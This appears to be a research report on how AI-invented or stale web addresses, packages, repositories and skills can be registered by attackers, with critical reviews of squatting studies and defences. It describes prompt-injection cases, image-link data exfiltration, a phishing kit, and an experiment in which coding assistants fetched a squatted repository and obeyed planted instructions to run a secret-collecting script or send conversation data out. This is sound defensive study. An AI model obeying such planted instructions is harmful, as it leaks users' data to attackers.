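# Security risks from AI-generated content on the live internet, and how well threat taxonomies cover them

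## How a model's output reaches the live internet

Language models write text that people and programs then use on the internet. A chatbot's answer contains a link, and a reader clicks it. A coding assistant writes a program that sends data to a web service. A company publishes a page that a model drafted, or lets a model send messages and place orders itself. Such output can do harm, and how much depends partly on the state of the internet at the time, such as who owns the linked site or runs the web service.

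A model's answer can send a bank's customer to a stranger's website because an address in the text belongs to someone other than the bank, or will by the time the customer uses it. This can happen without harmful code in the text or tampering with the model. It therefore need not involve either of two more familiar risks, malware (harmful software) and dependency-chain attacks, which reach a program through a component that the program declares and installs.

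A *live reference* is an address or name in a model's output that a person or program will look up on the internet. Live references include web addresses (URLs), API endpoints (web addresses to which programs, rather than people, send requests), and the names of code repositories, software packages and skills. Skills are packages of instructions, sometimes with code, that extend an AI system and that users install from a public directory. A *hallucinated reference* is a live reference that the model made up and that matches either nothing real or something other than what the user asked for.

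### How a model writes an address

A model produces text in tokens, chunks about the size of a word or part of a word. At each step it computes a probability for every token that could come next, given all the text so far. The software picks one, adds it to the text and repeats the step. The model writes web addresses by this same procedure, which does not check whether they exist. After "https://" and the name of a bank, ".com" is likely to come next, and then "/login" if the question was about logging in.

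OpenAI's post *Why language models hallucinate* (2025) offers an explanation that also applies to web addresses, though the post does not discuss them. Spelling errors disappear as models grow because spelling follows consistent patterns, but a model of any size that has to produce a pet's birthday will often be wrong, because birthdays follow no pattern. A particular bank's choice between two plausible names is about as arbitrary as a birthday, but the form of an address is as regular as spelling, so invented addresses tend to look right. The paper behind the post, *Why Language Models Hallucinate* (Kalai, Nachum and colleagues, 2025), adds that training and evaluation reward guessing over admitting uncertainty, which helps explain why a model offers an address when it could decline.

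With web search, a model can copy an address from a search result instead of composing one. Anthropic's documentation for Claude's search function, *Web search tool*, describes three steps. The model decides from the user's request whether to search, Anthropic's system runs the search and returns results with their URLs and titles, and the model writes an answer that cites them. But the model may not search, and Anthropic lists "coding concepts" among the subjects that Claude answers directly, though code often contains addresses. Amani, Lee and colleagues (2026) observed in *Characterizing Web Search by Conversational LLM Agents* that even when a chatbot does search, a small share of the addresses it cites comes from outside the results. A search result also proves only that a page exists, and the page's owner may be a fraudster.

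### Who can own which part of an address

Whether an outsider can exploit a wrong address depends on which part is wrong. The terms below follow web.dev, a guide for developers, and use the address https://login.example.com/start as the example.

| Part | In the example | Who controls it |
|---|---|---|
| Path | /start | Whoever runs the site |
| Subdomain | login | Whoever holds the registrable domain |
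| Registrable domain | example.com | Whoever registers it, for as long as they renew it |
| Public suffix | com | The registry; customers register names beneath it |

The *registrable domain* is the part of a domain name that somebody can buy. It usually consists of the public suffix and one label before it. Suffixes vary in length, so a registrable domain under com.au has three parts, as in example.com.au. The buyer, or registrant, gets the name through a registrar, a company accredited by ICANN, the body that coordinates domain names worldwide.

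When a model gets the path wrong on a bank's real domain, the customer sees an error page, and no outsider can put anything else there. An invented subdomain of the bank's domain is normally just as useless to an outsider. But an invented registrable domain is for sale, and registering one to receive the visitors that models send is called *phantom squatting*.

On a shared platform, an attacker may be able to claim a made-up address without owning the domain. An address on the code-hosting site GitHub consists of github.com, an account name and a repository name. Anyone can open an account under an unused name, so a made-up path there may be available to whoever registers the account first. Li and Gao (2025), in *Investigating Security Implications of Automatically Generated Code on the Software Supply Chain*, count invented GitHub accounts among the things an attacker can claim in advance,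 along with domains and packages.

### Agents and hidden instructions

An *agent* is a model connected to software tools that carry out its output. The model writes a request in an agreed format, such as to open a page or run a command. The program around the model, often called the harness, recognises the request, performs the operation and adds the result to the text the model continues from. This loop may repeat many times without anyone watching. Zhang, Li and colleagues (2026), in *From AI-Generated Content to Agentic Action*, describe the move to agents as a shift from producing content to executing operations, and mention file access, credential retrieval, code execution and financial operations that may happen before a human reviewer intervenes. Some agents work in a programmer's files and command line, while others use ordinary websites by clicking and typing.

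A model receives both its user's request and the content of a fetched page as text, and it can't reliably tell its user's instructions from those a stranger wrote into the page. In *indirect prompt injection*, an attacker exploits this by hiding instructions in content that a model will read, and the model follows them as if they came from its user. Kumari's *What is AI squatting* lists documents, emails and websites as the usual carriers. For example, a page of train times might contain an instruction to look up the user's calendar and send it to a certain address, written in white on a white background so that a person reading the page wouldn't notice it.

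Sending data out requires an address, so one defence is to limit which addresses an agent may open. In the autumn of 2025, Anthropic's *Web fetch tool* documentation said that Claude could not open addresses it had constructed itself, only those that the user had supplied or that earlier searches and fetches had returned. Willison (2025), a software developer who writes about this class of attack, had hoped for a stricter rule that allowed only addresses from the user's own messages. Under Anthropic's rule, an agent may still be able to open a link from a hostile page. The rule also prevents the agent from opening hallucinated addresses through this tool, though an agent with a command line has other ways to reach the internet.

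### Four routes from output to harm

The simplest route is that *a person or program follows a live reference*. This can happen seconds or years after the model produced the reference. *Phantom Squatting*, a 2026 report from Unit 42, the research group of the security company Palo Alto Networks, lists some of the users: agents that retrieve the address directly, developers who build it into production code, and automated systems that write it into documentation. Code can also make programs follow a reference repeatedly. Li and Gao point out that a web page can include a JavaScript library by URL alone, with no installation step. Browsers then request that address as people visit the page, and run whatever its owner is serving.

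On the second route, *software displays or runs the output at once*. Many chat windows turn a model's plain text into formatted text with pictures. To show a picture, the browser requests it from the address in the text, and any data in that address goes to the server with the request. A script in a generated web page can also start when the page opens. Neither requires a click, so a careful reader who might hesitate over a link has no chance to do so.

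A model's output can also do harm when somebody publishes it and others read it. People post a model's answers as blog posts, forum replies or technical documentation, and search engines and other models then pick them up. The person harmed may never have used a language model. Correcting the model afterwards does not remove the copies already published.

Finally, *an agent acts on a real site*, for example by posting a comment, sending a message, buying something or deleting a file. In this case the address may be correct, and the harm comes from the agent's action.

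One incident can involve more than one route. An agent that downloads a repository whose name a model invented has followed a live reference, and may then act on instructions it finds inside. It is still useful to distinguish the routes because each allows intervention at a different point. A browser can warn about a link before the user clicks it, and a chat window can refuse to load outside images. For published text, the last good time to intervene is before publication, and for an agent, it is when the agent is given permission to act.

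### One address, four fates

Take an invented case. The owner of an online shop asks a coding assistant for a program that looks up the price of sending a parcel, and the assistant's answer includes these lines:

```
requests.post("https://api.parcelrates.example/v1/quote",
              headers={"Authorization": SHOP_KEY},
              json={"deliver_to": customer_address})
```

The program sends the shop's secret key and a customer's address to a server, which should return a price. (The server's domain name ends in .example, which nobody can register, in place of an ordinary ending such as .com.) Four things may be true of that server.

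- The address is correct. Parcel Rates is an honest company and this is where it answers requests.
- The address is real but hostile. A fraudster set up the service and wrote convincing instructions for it, which the model saw in training or found by search. The server returns plausible prices and keeps the keys and the customers' addresses.
- Nobody has registered the domain. The program fails with an error, and the shop owner may shrug and leave it for later. Then a stranger buys the name, and the program starts to work.
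- The address is correct today and belongs to someone else next year. Parcel Rates closes, or sells the name, or forgets to renew it. The shop's program goes on sending keys and addresses to the new owner, and nobody has changed a character of it.

The last case requires nothing unusual, since domain names routinely expire. ICANN (2017) sets out the timetable for generic endings such as .com. The registrar may allow up to 45 days after expiry for renewal. Once it deletes the name, the registrant has 30 days to recover it, and the name is released 5 days after that period ends. A lapsed name therefore becomes "available for registration by any third-party" (ICANN, 2017) between 35 and 80 days after it expires.

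The text is the same in all four cases, so a scanner that reads only the program must return the same verdict each time. A verdict of "safe" is wrong about the fraudster's server, and a verdict of "unsafe" is wrong about the honest company's. A better scanner cannot solve this, because the deciding fact is not in the text. By contrast, a password typed into the code is a flaw that any reader of the program can find. A scanner can use signs in the text of an address, such as a misspelt brand name, to estimate the odds that it is unsafe, but not to settle the question.

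Looking up the address works better, up to a point. A lookup immediately shows whether the domain is unregistered, and it may reveal a fraudulent site if somebody has already reported it. It cannot show that a domain will later be sold, so checking the address when the model writes the code does not replace checking it when the code runs.

The example also shows that an address can be dangerous without being hallucinated, since the model made up only the unregistered one. Li and Gao use the term *dangling reference* for any reference to an expired or non-existent domain or package, and an attacker can take over either kind. The difference matters for correcting models, and *Detecting and Correcting Reference Hallucinations in Commercial LLMs and Deep Research Agents* (2026) distinguishes the two using the Wayback Machine, a public archive of old web pages. A dead address with an archived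 copy has gone stale, while one without a copy probably never existed.

### What it takes for a taxonomy to cover a risk

A *threat taxonomy* is a published scheme that names and sorts attacks, weaknesses or risks. It gives companies a common vocabulary, so two that suffer the same attack can report it under the same label. Security teams also use it to check whether they have a defence for each entry. The best-known schemes come from MITRE, an American non-profit research organisation, OWASP, a foundation for software security, and NIST, the US government's standards agency. The schemes serve different purposes. Zhang and colleagues describe the OWASP Top 10 for LLM Applications as an operational checklist that is not meant to be a scholarly taxonomy. A list of ten leaves things out on purpose, so a gap in it is weaker evidence that a risk was overlooked than a gap in a catalogue meant to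 be complete.

*Coverage* is a matter of four tests:

1. The taxonomy has an entry that names the risk, in words that fit it without stretching.
2. The entry separates the risk from similar ones that call for different handling.
3. The entry comes with a defence that would work against this risk.
4. People who record incidents can file them under the entry and count them later.

A scheme can pass some of these tests and fail others. A very broad entry, such as "false output", would cover every hallucinated address but give a defender no information about domain registration. Counting attacks is also difficult. The OECD's *AI-Hallucinated Domains Enable New Cyberattacks via Phantom Squatting* (2026) is a single entry in that organisation's monitor of AI incidents, but it concerns a technique that several attackers may have used on several targets, so counting such entries would not give the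 number of attacks.

The six cases used to apply the tests differ in who uses the output, whether the address or name is real, and whether anyone intends harm.

1. A chatbot gives a user a hallucinated domain as the address of their bank.
2. An agent clones, that is downloads, a repository whose name the model hallucinated.
3. A coding assistant writes a program that calls an API endpoint run by scammers.
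4. A chatbot's answer contains an image link with a secret in its address, and the image loads by itself, which sends the secret to the owner of the server.
5. A model invents a package name, and published AI text spreads it. There is no attacker.
6. An agent publishes something harmful on a real site, unprompted.

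## Invented web addresses that attackers can register

In the first of the six test cases, a chatbot invents a domain and gives it to a bank's customer. The customer usually gets an error message, but in phantom squatting an attacker has already registered the domain, so the customer reaches a working website.

### How the attack works

An attacker begins by asking chatbots the questions a customer would ask. Suppose a bank called Northmere has its real site at northmere.example. The attacker asks several chatbots where a small company can apply for a Northmere card, where its accountant can log in, and where it can raise a payment limit. They repeat these questions in hundreds of wordings and record every domain in the answers. Some of those domains belong to the bank, but others, such as northmere-business.example, may be unregistered.

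The attacker then looks for names that recur, since a name that turns up once in ten thousand answers will bring few visitors. Unit 42, which coined the term phantom squatting, looks for names that a model repeats at different settings of *temperature*, which controls how random the choice of each token is. At a low temperature the model nearly always picks the most likely token, so a name that appears even then is close to its standard answer. Unit 42 also looks for names that several models produce for the same question, because these can reach users of more than one chatbot.

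The evidence that separate models invent the same names is mixed. Li and Gao compared the hallucinated domains of four older models and found an average overlap of only 0.70%. Studies of other kinds of names found more agreement. *Skills That Don't Exist* (2026) reports that models from different families converge on the same invented skill names, and *Beware of Agentic Botnets* (2026) describes shared patterns in the invented repository addresses that enable HalluSquatting, the equivalent attack on code repositories. These results are compatible if most invented names are one-offs and a few recur across models. The average overlap would then be tiny, but an attacker would need only the recurring names.

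Registering a domain costs little and takes minutes. The attacker puts a copy of the bank's login page there and waits for chatbots to send visitors. Some visitors may be AI agents, which Unit 42 considers the most serious targets. An agent may process whatever the page returns, including hidden instructions, before anyone checks it, whereas a person still has to type a password or download a file.

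### Why a new domain passes the filters

Many web filters check a domain against lists of reported sites, feeds of domains that analysts have seen in attacks, and scores that build up as a site attracts traffic. A newly registered domain has no such record, so these filters have no basis for blocking it.

Every new phishing site has this advantage for a while. But an ordinary phisher also has to deliver the link, usually in an email or text message that another filter can inspect. In phantom squatting, the link arrives in an answer from a chatbot that the victim's employer may have approved.

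Attackers can do damage before a new domain has a record. Unit 42 observed domains that hosted malicious content within hours of registration, and in one case the attacker had put the fake site on a server before buying the domain. Attackers can also prolong this period by showing a harmless page to automated scanners and the fraudulent one to people. A filter that treated all new domains as suspect would raise mostly false alarms. Palo Alto Networks detects more than 200,000 newly registered domains a day, according to a Unit 42 article on AI-themed domains.

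### A small test with login pages

Netcraft, a company that finds fraudulent websites and has them taken down, asked models of the GPT-4.1 family where to log in to 50 brands. The questions were worded as if they came from someone who had lost a bookmark or wanted to be sure of reaching the official site. *Large Language Models (LLMs) Are Falling for Phishing Scams* reports that the models returned 131 hostnames (full names, including any subdomain) on 97 domains. Of these domains, 64 belonged to the right brand, 28 were unregistered, parked or inactive, and 5 belonged to unrelated businesses.

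So 34% of the domains were not the brand's own. This figure is often misapplied. In its opening paragraph, Netcraft itself applies it to the 131 hostnames rather than to the domains, as does Security Boulevard's *Report Finds LLMs Are Prone to Be Exploited by Phishing Campaigns* (2025). The test also counts each distinct domain once, however often it came up, so the figure doesn't support Netcraft's conclusion that over a third of users might end up on somebody else's site. If a model gave the right address 98 times and two different wrong ones once each, two-thirds of its distinct domains would be wrong, yet 98% of users would reach the right site. The 28 inactive domains also include parked ones, which an attacker would have to buy from their current owners.

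The test shows that a model can give a domain that an outsider could acquire even when the question contains no trick. Netcraft adds that regional banks and credit unions fared worse than global brands, presumably because less about them appears in training data. It gives no separate figures for them.

In its most striking example, Perplexity, a search engine built on language models, answered a question about Wells Fargo's login page with a link to a fraudulent copy on Google Sites, a free hosting service. This is a different problem from attackers registering invented domains, because the page already existed and the search had found it.

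### Unit 42's large study

Unit 42's study, published on June 30, 2026, covers 913 brands. A program gathered information on each brand's products, customer portals and developer resources, generated questions about them and removed near-duplicates, which left 685,339 prompts. The researchers ran these at three temperatures on two small, cheap, unnamed models, one from April 2025 and one from June 2025. They collected 2.1 million distinct URLs and checked whether each one led anywhere and whether threat databases listed it.

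| Result | URLs | Share of all URLs |
|---|---|---|
| Flagged as malicious | 13,229 | 0.61% |
| High risk, for example parked or nearly empty pages | 41,313 | 1.90% |
| Did not resolve | 809,455 | 37.28% |

The share of URLs that did not resolve was 43.1% at the highest temperature, 32.5% at the middle one and 34.6% at the lowest, so lowering the temperature did not solve the problem. The choice of model made a bigger difference, with 44.6% of URLs unresolved for the older model and 27.5% for the newer one.

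These rates don't measure what ordinary users see, because Unit 42 wrote its prompts to provoke errors, partly by exploiting models' tendency to accept false premises. One prompt asks for the payment gateway sandbox (a test version of a payment system) of a postal marketplace, which can lead a model to supply an address whether or not the sandbox exists. The researchers also ignored answers without a URL, so a model that gave no URL for nine questions out of ten would get the same error rate as one that gave a URL for every question, if their URLs were equally bad.

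The 13,229 malicious URLs need separate treatment, since they were already dangerous when the models produced them. Unit 42 argues that the models cannot have learned its malicious domains from training data, because attackers registered them after both models came out. But it gives registration dates for only a handful of domains, and one of those dates contradicts the argument. Some of the 13,229 URLs may be real addresses that the models repeated.

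### How many invented domains are for sale

Unit 42 says that the 809,455 unresolved URLs contain about 250,000 unregistered domains that an attacker could buy, but its own breakdown of those URLs suggests a much smaller number. It says the model invented a page on a registered domain in 49.7% of them, a subdomain of an existing domain in 39.5%, and the whole domain in the remaining 10.8%, about 87,630 URLs. Several URLs can share a domain, so this last group should contain at most 87,630 domains for sale.

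The 250,000 may be the number of distinct domains behind all the unresolved URLs, including domains that already have owners. If so, the headline figure is at least 2.8 times too high.

Another possibility is that the breakdown sorts URLs by their form instead of by which part is false. An address such as admin.northmere-business.example would then count as an invented subdomain even if nobody owned northmere-business.example. The published examples give this some support, since they begin with "admin", "billing" and "sandbox", and the domains that follow were unregistered when the models wrote them. The large share of invented pages is odd in any case. The DNS lookup that turns a domain name into a server's network address ignores everything after the domain, so a made-up page on a working site would still resolve. If the categories describe only form, 250,000 may be right. Without the underlying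 data, it is safer to say that the two models invented tens of thousands of registrable domains, and perhaps as many as 250,000.

Even the lower figure is about 4% of all URLs. Li and Gao also found invented or expired domains in generated code, where they made up between 1.67% and 3.35% of domains, depending on the model. They checked with the registrar GoDaddy whether each domain was available, but the models they used, including GPT-3.5, are now old.

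### Six domains that criminals registered

Unit 42 put the unregistered names on a watchlist and monitored new registrations for matches. It describes six cases, with the brands' names removed.

| Target | Form of the domain name | Registration |
|---|---|---|
| Postal service's online marketplace | Similar to the marketplace's own | 23 days after the prediction |
| Postal delivery service | Brand plus "post-app" | 51 days after |
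| Sports betting operator | Brand plus "-login" | 45 days after |
| Competing betting operator | Brand plus "-es" | 40 days after |
| European retail bank | Brand plus "empresas" (companies) | 35 days after, and not for the first time |
| Commercial bank in the UAE | Brand plus "business" | 11 months before |

The postal marketplace is the most detailed case. On March 8, 2026, the two models produced 13 URLs on a domain that resembled the marketplace's, some of them at the lowest temperature. On March 31, someone registered the domain and installed Montana Empire, a phishing kit (a ready-made package for running a fraudulent site). Unit 42 detected the registration the same day.

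The kit copied products from the real marketplace as they changed. It collected card details and national identity documents. Victims could also pay by bank transfer instead of by card, and the criminals could change the account numbers through the messaging service Telegram. An operator could use a control panel to relay the one-time codes that victims received from their banks. The attacker had left an AI coding assistant's project folder in the kit, and session logs recorded the assistant helping to copy the shop and write the server software.

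The logs show that the attacker built the site with an AI assistant, but nothing in the published account shows that the attacker got the domain name from one. The logs therefore don't support Unit 42's conclusion that its models and the attacker arrived at the name by the same mechanism. A name that resembles a well-known marketplace is an obvious choice for anyone who wants to impersonate it.

The UAE bank case is even weaker evidence that attackers harvest names from models. A criminal registered that domain on April 1, 2025 and used it to steal login details from company administrators. The older of the two models came out sometime in April 2025 and the newer one in June, so the criminal almost certainly got the name elsewhere. Unit 42 presents the case as proof that the invented name was inevitable. It does suggest that people and models can produce the same name independently, but if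 so, a match in the other cases doesn't show that the criminals used a model.

### How many matches to expect by chance

Phishers have long combined brand names with words such as "login" or "support" in domain names. Security researchers call this *combosquatting*, and *Can LLMs Reason About Brand Ownership?* (Mashood and Nabeel, 2026) lists it among the standard ways to imitate a brand. Five of the six domains in the table fit the pattern. A model guessing the address of a bank's business portal also combines the brand with a likely word, so a long list of its guesses will overlap with the names that criminals choose on their own.

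The expected number of matches from this overlap is the length of the watchlist multiplied by the probability that a phisher registers any given name on it during the period. Nobody has published that probability. If it were one in 20,000 over two months, a watchlist of 250,000 names would produce about 12 matches even if no phisher consulted a model. Phishers register enough domains for chance matches to be plausible. GBHackers' *Threat Actors Register Over 26,000 Domains Imitating Brands to Deceive Users* (2025) reports a count, also by Unit 42, of 26,328 domains for text-message scams in March 2025 alone.

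The six cases are examples, and Unit 42 does not give the total number of watchlist names registered or say how many of those registrations were harmless. Its measure of lead time also depends on when it started querying the models. The 23 days are counted from when its pipeline first produced the marketplace domain, but the models had been available since the previous year.

Researchers could compare the models' list with one of equal length, made by a simple rule that attaches common words to the same brand names, and count the malicious registrations on each. If criminals registered more names from the models' list, that would be evidence that they use models to choose domains, or at least that models are good at predicting their choices.

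*The Range Shrinks, the Threat Remains* (Churilov, 2026) makes a related comparison for slopsquatting, the equivalent attack with software packages. Churilov's list of invented package names had been public by accident for six months. In that time, somebody registered about 1% of the names, the same rate as for names he had not published. This tests a narrower question, whether publication attracts attackers, but it includes a comparison group, which the domain study lacks.

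The cases do show that a watchlist of model-invented names can catch some fraudulent sites on the day they appear, before they have a reputation. They also show that models can produce a domain that a criminal later owns. A chatbot that still produces that domain will send people to the criminal's site, however the criminal chose the name.

Unit 42 reports no victim who followed a model's link to any of the six domains. The machine-written summary in the OECD's incident monitor nevertheless says that phantom squatting has resulted in credential theft. The phishing sites were real and may well have collected passwords, but it is not known how any victims reached them.

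People click on invented addresses. *How Often Do AI Assistants Hallucinate Links?*, a study by the marketing software company Ahrefs, examined visits that AI assistants had sent to websites. About 1% of the distinct addresses that received visitors from ChatGPT led to a "not found" page, and the rate was lower for the other assistants. These were missing pages on existing sites. The method cannot detect visits to unregistered domains, which are the ones that matter for phantom squatting, because those domains have no site to record visitors.

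### Models with live search

Live search should make AI tools less likely to invent web addresses, but early products still produced many bad links. The Columbia Journalism Review tested eight AI search tools in 2025, and more than half of the answers from Gemini and Grok 3 contained invented or broken links, according to Search Engine Land.

A larger study from April 2026, *Detecting and Correcting Reference Hallucinations in Commercial LLMs and Deep Research Agents* by Rao, Wong and Callison-Burch, found lower rates. It checked the links in answers from ten search-equipped systems, mostly from 2025, and counted a URL as invented if it was dead and had no archived copy. By that test, between 3% and 13% of each system's URLs were invented. The average was 10.7% for "deep research" agents, which run many searches and write a long report, and 4.8% for models that ran a simple search. The agents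 differed widely, with OpenAI's at 3.5% and Google's at 13.3%.

The study counts invented pages on real sites together with invented domains, so it doesn't show how many of these addresses an attacker could register. If the 10.8% from the phantom squatting study applied here, between 0.3% and 1.4% of cited URLs would have an unregistered domain. This is a rough guess, because the 10.8% comes from different models, provocative prompts and a disputed breakdown.

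A model can invent more domains when its search tool fails than when it has no search tool. Mashood and Nabeel asked four models to list exactly 50 domains belonging to each of 36 frequently imitated brands. Without search, 74% of the domains that Gemini 2.5 Flash listed were genuine. With search, only 5% were, because the tool timed out for most brands and the model filled the list with plausible names that did not exist. The newer Gemini 3.5 Flash improved slightly with search, from 77% to 80%. Asking for exactly 50 names encourages guessing, and few users would ask for that. But search tools also fail in ordinary use, and the user may not be able to tell that an answer came from the model's memory.

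### Defences

Unit 42 recommends *watchlists* of invented domains, and it calls finding the names in advance the only approach that addresses the problem at its root. Its parent company sells such filtering, and the study advertises the company's products at the beginning and end. Still, watchlists have a clear advantage over reputation checks, because a filter can examine a listed domain as soon as somebody registers it. The list must be updated constantly, because new models will produce new names.

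A match on the list may also be legitimate. Companies register lookalike domains themselves, either to keep criminals from using them or for new products, and Mashood and Nabeel tested whether models could tell these apart from fraudulent ones. Without looking anything up, the models misclassified between 74% and 92% of the brands' own domains as not belonging to them. When the models could consult WHOIS, the public record of who registered a domain, this fell to between 20% and 33%. Part of that improvement comes from the test's design, because the researchers also used WHOIS to decide which domains belonged to a brand. Some owners also hide their names in the record.

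*Defensive registration* means that the bank buys the invented names before attackers do, and keeps renewing them. Models produced 250,000 names for 913 brands, an average of about 274 each, which would cost a brand $2,740 a year at an assumed $10 per name. Netcraft, which sells monitoring and takedowns, calls defensive registration impractical because the possible variations are infinite. No company could buy every name that a future model might invent, but it could buy the few that recur. For invented skills, the 500 most common names accounted for 57% of the cases in one experiment in *Skills That Don't Exist*. Nobody has published the same figure for domains.

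*Checking the address before showing it* moves the work to the company that runs the chatbot. Rao and colleagues gave three models a tool that requests each URL and, if the page is missing, looks for an archived copy, then let them correct their answers. The share of dead links fell from 16.0% to 0.6% for GPT-5.1, from 6.1% to 0.1% for Gemini 2.5 Pro and from 4.9% to 0.8% for Claude Sonnet 4.5. A much smaller model, GPT-5 nano, called the tool but kept proposing addresses that it had marked as dead.

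This lookup works only until an attacker registers the address. Once a phishing page is up, the chatbot has to determine whether the page is genuine, and relying on the model to judge this is risky. *ClaimMirage* (2026) examines how claims in a domain name, which its owner can choose freely, change a model's judgment of whether the domain is a threat. In *MalURLBench* (2026), disguised malicious addresses often deceived the 12 models tested.

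A domain's registration date is harder to fake. A model's training data cannot describe a site that did not exist when the data ended. If the model produces a domain without looking it up, and WHOIS shows that the domain was registered after the training data ended, the name is probably either a guess or an old name that has changed hands, and the chatbot should withhold it. This test would have flagged the fake postal marketplace on its first day, which came nine months after the newer model's release. A squatter could still evade the test by buying a name and waiting for the next generation of models, whose training data will end after the purchase.

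## Invented repositories, skills and packages that agents fetch

Security researchers worried about invented software packages before they worried about invented domains. Programmers build much of today's software from packages that strangers publish in open registries, mainly PyPI for Python and npm for JavaScript. Installing a package takes a short command containing its name, and the package's code may run immediately. If a model made up the name, the command normally fails. In *slopsquatting*, an attacker has already published a package under that name, so the command installs the attacker's code. Publishing is free, and according to Churilov, neither registry reviews a first upload.

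### How often models invent packages

Spracklen, Wijewickrama and colleagues (2024), in *We Have a Package for You!*, had 16 models write 576,000 samples of Python and JavaScript code. The study, which appeared at the USENIX Security conference in 2025, is the usual source for the size of the problem. The models named 2.23 million packages, and 440,445 of these names (19.7%) were missing from the registries. The 19.7% is a share of package mentions, not code samples. Socket, a software security company, gives the unit correctly in its summary but then says that the two worst models hallucinated in over a third of "outputs", although the study's rates for individual models are also shares of packages.

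The 19.7% average also combines commercial models, at 5.2%, with open-source ones, at 21.7%. It depends, too, on how the researchers collected the names. Only 7% of the outputs contained an installation command, so the researchers also asked each model twice per sample which packages the task needed, and such questions encourage guessing. When Li and Gao put ordinary coding questions to GPT-4o-mini, 8.36% of the Python packages it named were invented, compared with 37.09% when they asked it to recommend a package. The 19.7% figure therefore probably overstates how often invented packages appear in ordinary code, though a programmer whose program won't start may well ask a model what to install.

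To exploit invented package names, an attacker needs ones that models produce repeatedly. Spracklen et al. took 500 prompts that had produced an invented package and ran each one ten more times. The same invented name reappeared in all ten runs for 43% of the prompts and in none of them for 39%.

Churilov ran the same set of prompts on five newer models, including Claude Sonnet 4.6 and GPT-5.4-mini. Between 3.6% and 5.0% of their package mentions were invented, no better than the 3.59% that Spracklen and colleagues measured for GPT-4 Turbo. Unlike earlier open-weight models, DeepSeek V3.2 did no worse than the others in the group. Small models still do worse. In *Evaluating Inference-Time Defenses Against Package Hallucination in LLM-Generated Code* (2026), a small Qwen model named 100,896 packages, of which 48,330 did not exist.

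The ranking of models in these newer results also depends on the unit of measurement. Of Churilov's five models, GPT-5.4-mini had the highest share of package mentions that were invented (5.02%) but the lowest share of answers containing an invented package (2.15%). It gave no usable code for almost a third of the prompts, and an answer without code can't contain an invented package.

Hallucinated packages are also easy to miscount, because the name a Python program uses to load a package often differs from the name used to install it. Churilov's earlier versions counted some correct code as hallucinated for this reason. Fixing this and some smaller errors lowered every model's hallucination rate by about a fifth.

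After the corrections, all five models had invented 104 of the 2,282 distinct names. These are under 5% of the names, but they account for 42% of the times that a model used an invented name (2,699 of 6,363). The evidence on domains was mixed but pointed to the same pattern. An attacker could not register all 104, because PyPI blocks some names and four of the npm names are in a namespace that belongs to an organisation.

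People do install packages with invented names. Spracklen's team describes an earlier experiment in which a researcher, Lanyado, published one, and other people downloaded it and built it into their own software. Evidence of actual attacks is weaker. At least 23 of the names that Churilov's models suggested had once hosted malware, and someone registered another with malware after the test. But more than half of the 104 shared names are one character away from a real package, so criminals who exploit typing errors might also choose them. The malware therefore does not show that anyone got a name from a model.

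### Invented accounts and build plugins

In some programming languages, a package's name is a web address, so a model that invents a package also invents a repository. *Secure or Suspect?* (2025) examined packages for the language Go, many of which are on GitHub. More than half of the github.com addresses that the tested models wrote contained an invented account or repository name.

Li and Gao tested four models, GPT-3.5 Turbo, GPT-4o-mini and two versions of Llama 3.1, for several kinds of invented names. They collected about 105,000 coding questions from Stack Overflow, asked each one in four ways, and added 20,010 requests for the configuration files that control automatic building and testing. Depending on the model, between 5.83% and 18.04% of the GitHub accounts in the answers did not exist, a higher share than for domains. One domain in the answers had expired and was for sale. It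 had belonged to a JavaScript package that people still downloaded 433 times a week.

The configuration files were far worse. They name plugins by GitHub account and repository, and the build service downloads and runs whatever it finds there. Between 70% and 96% of the plugins did not exist. Of the accounts named for these missing plugins, 15% to 35% were free for anyone to register. One model attributed 26 plugins to a single invented account, so an attacker who registered that account could have supplied all of them.

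### Why "clone librepods" calls for a guess

HalluSquatting extends slopsquatting to repositories and skills. In slopsquatting, the attacker's code ends up in the software that the victim is writing, whereas in HalluSquatting the attacker's text reaches the agent itself, which may follow it as instructions. *Beware of Agentic Botnets*, by Aya Spira and five colleagues, calls such text *promptware*, meaning input designed to act like malware by exploiting the language model inside an application. Promptware can also be images or sound.

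Earlier promptware usually reached a chosen victim through an email, a calendar invitation or a shared document. An attacker without such a channel could put the malicious prompt on a web page, but few agents visit an obscure page, and altering a popular one requires breaking into its site. An attacker who registers a name that many agents will guess can reach them without breaking into anything.

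People remember the name of a GitHub project but often not the account it belongs to, and the project's address includes both. For example, librepods, a program that makes Apple's AirPods work with other companies' devices, belongs to the account kavishdevar, which no one could infer from the project's name. If a user tells an agent to "clone librepods" and the agent doesn't look up the account name, the model has to guess it.

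The download command needs a project's full address, so programmers used to search for the project, open its page and copy the address. There they could also see who owned the project, how many people had starred it (GitHub's equivalent of a bookmark) and what it would do when run. An agent that writes the address from memory skips this page and may run the project before anybody has read it.

### How often the models guessed wrong

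The researchers chose 16 projects: ten from 2025 that were on GitHub's trending list, five famous ones from 2013 to 2018, and librepods as a case study. They asked six models from Google, OpenAI and Anthropic to print the download command, 100 times for each project, without a search tool.

On average, 92.4% of the answers were wrong for the ten recent projects, against 0.9% for the five old ones. The researchers attribute this to training data, since a model can't have seen a project that began after its data ended. The exceptions fit this explanation. Claude Opus 4.5 always found the right owner for Archon and ui-tars-desktop, which both date from the first weeks of 2025. But the old projects are also much better known. Each has at least 180,000 stars, while the most popular recent one has about 51,000. The experiment can't separate the effect of age from that of fame, and models might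 do just as badly on an obscure project from 2015.

The paper gives the maximum rate at which models hallucinate repositories as 100% in its introduction but 85% in its abstract. The 100% refers to single combinations of a project and a model, and in 53 of the 60 combinations involving a recent project, the model never named the right owner. It is unclear where the 85% comes from. The closest figure is GPT-5.2's average of 85.7% over the ten recent projects, but four of the other five models had higher averages.

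Neither number measures the chance of an attack, because many wrong answers contained a placeholder such as "username" or an account that already belonged to someone else. In 27% of the answers about recent projects, the account did not exist and an attacker could have registered it.

The most useful pattern for an attacker is the project's name repeated as the account name, as in librepods/librepods. For five of the ten recent projects, this was the most common answer across the six models, at 23% to 35% of answers, and the account was available to register. An attacker could therefore register accounts named after trending projects without querying a model.

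### What the coding assistants did

The researchers then registered the account "librepods" and put a harmless copy of the project there. They asked six coding assistants to clone librepods, 20 times per test, and measured whether the assistant fetched the copy and whether it carried out hostile instructions planted among the project's files. Some instructions led the assistant to run a script that collected fake secret keys on the researchers' own machine. Others told it to use its own tools, for example to send a summary of the conversation to an outside server.

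| Assistant and model | Aim of the instructions | Fetched | Carried out | Overall |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Cursor, Sonnet 4.5 | Run a script | 7 of 20 | 5 of 7 | 25% |
| Cursor, GPT-5.2 Codex | Misuse a tool | 7 of 20 | 4 of 7 | 20% |
| Cursor CLI, Grok Code | Run a script | 17 of 20 | 6 of 17 | 30% |
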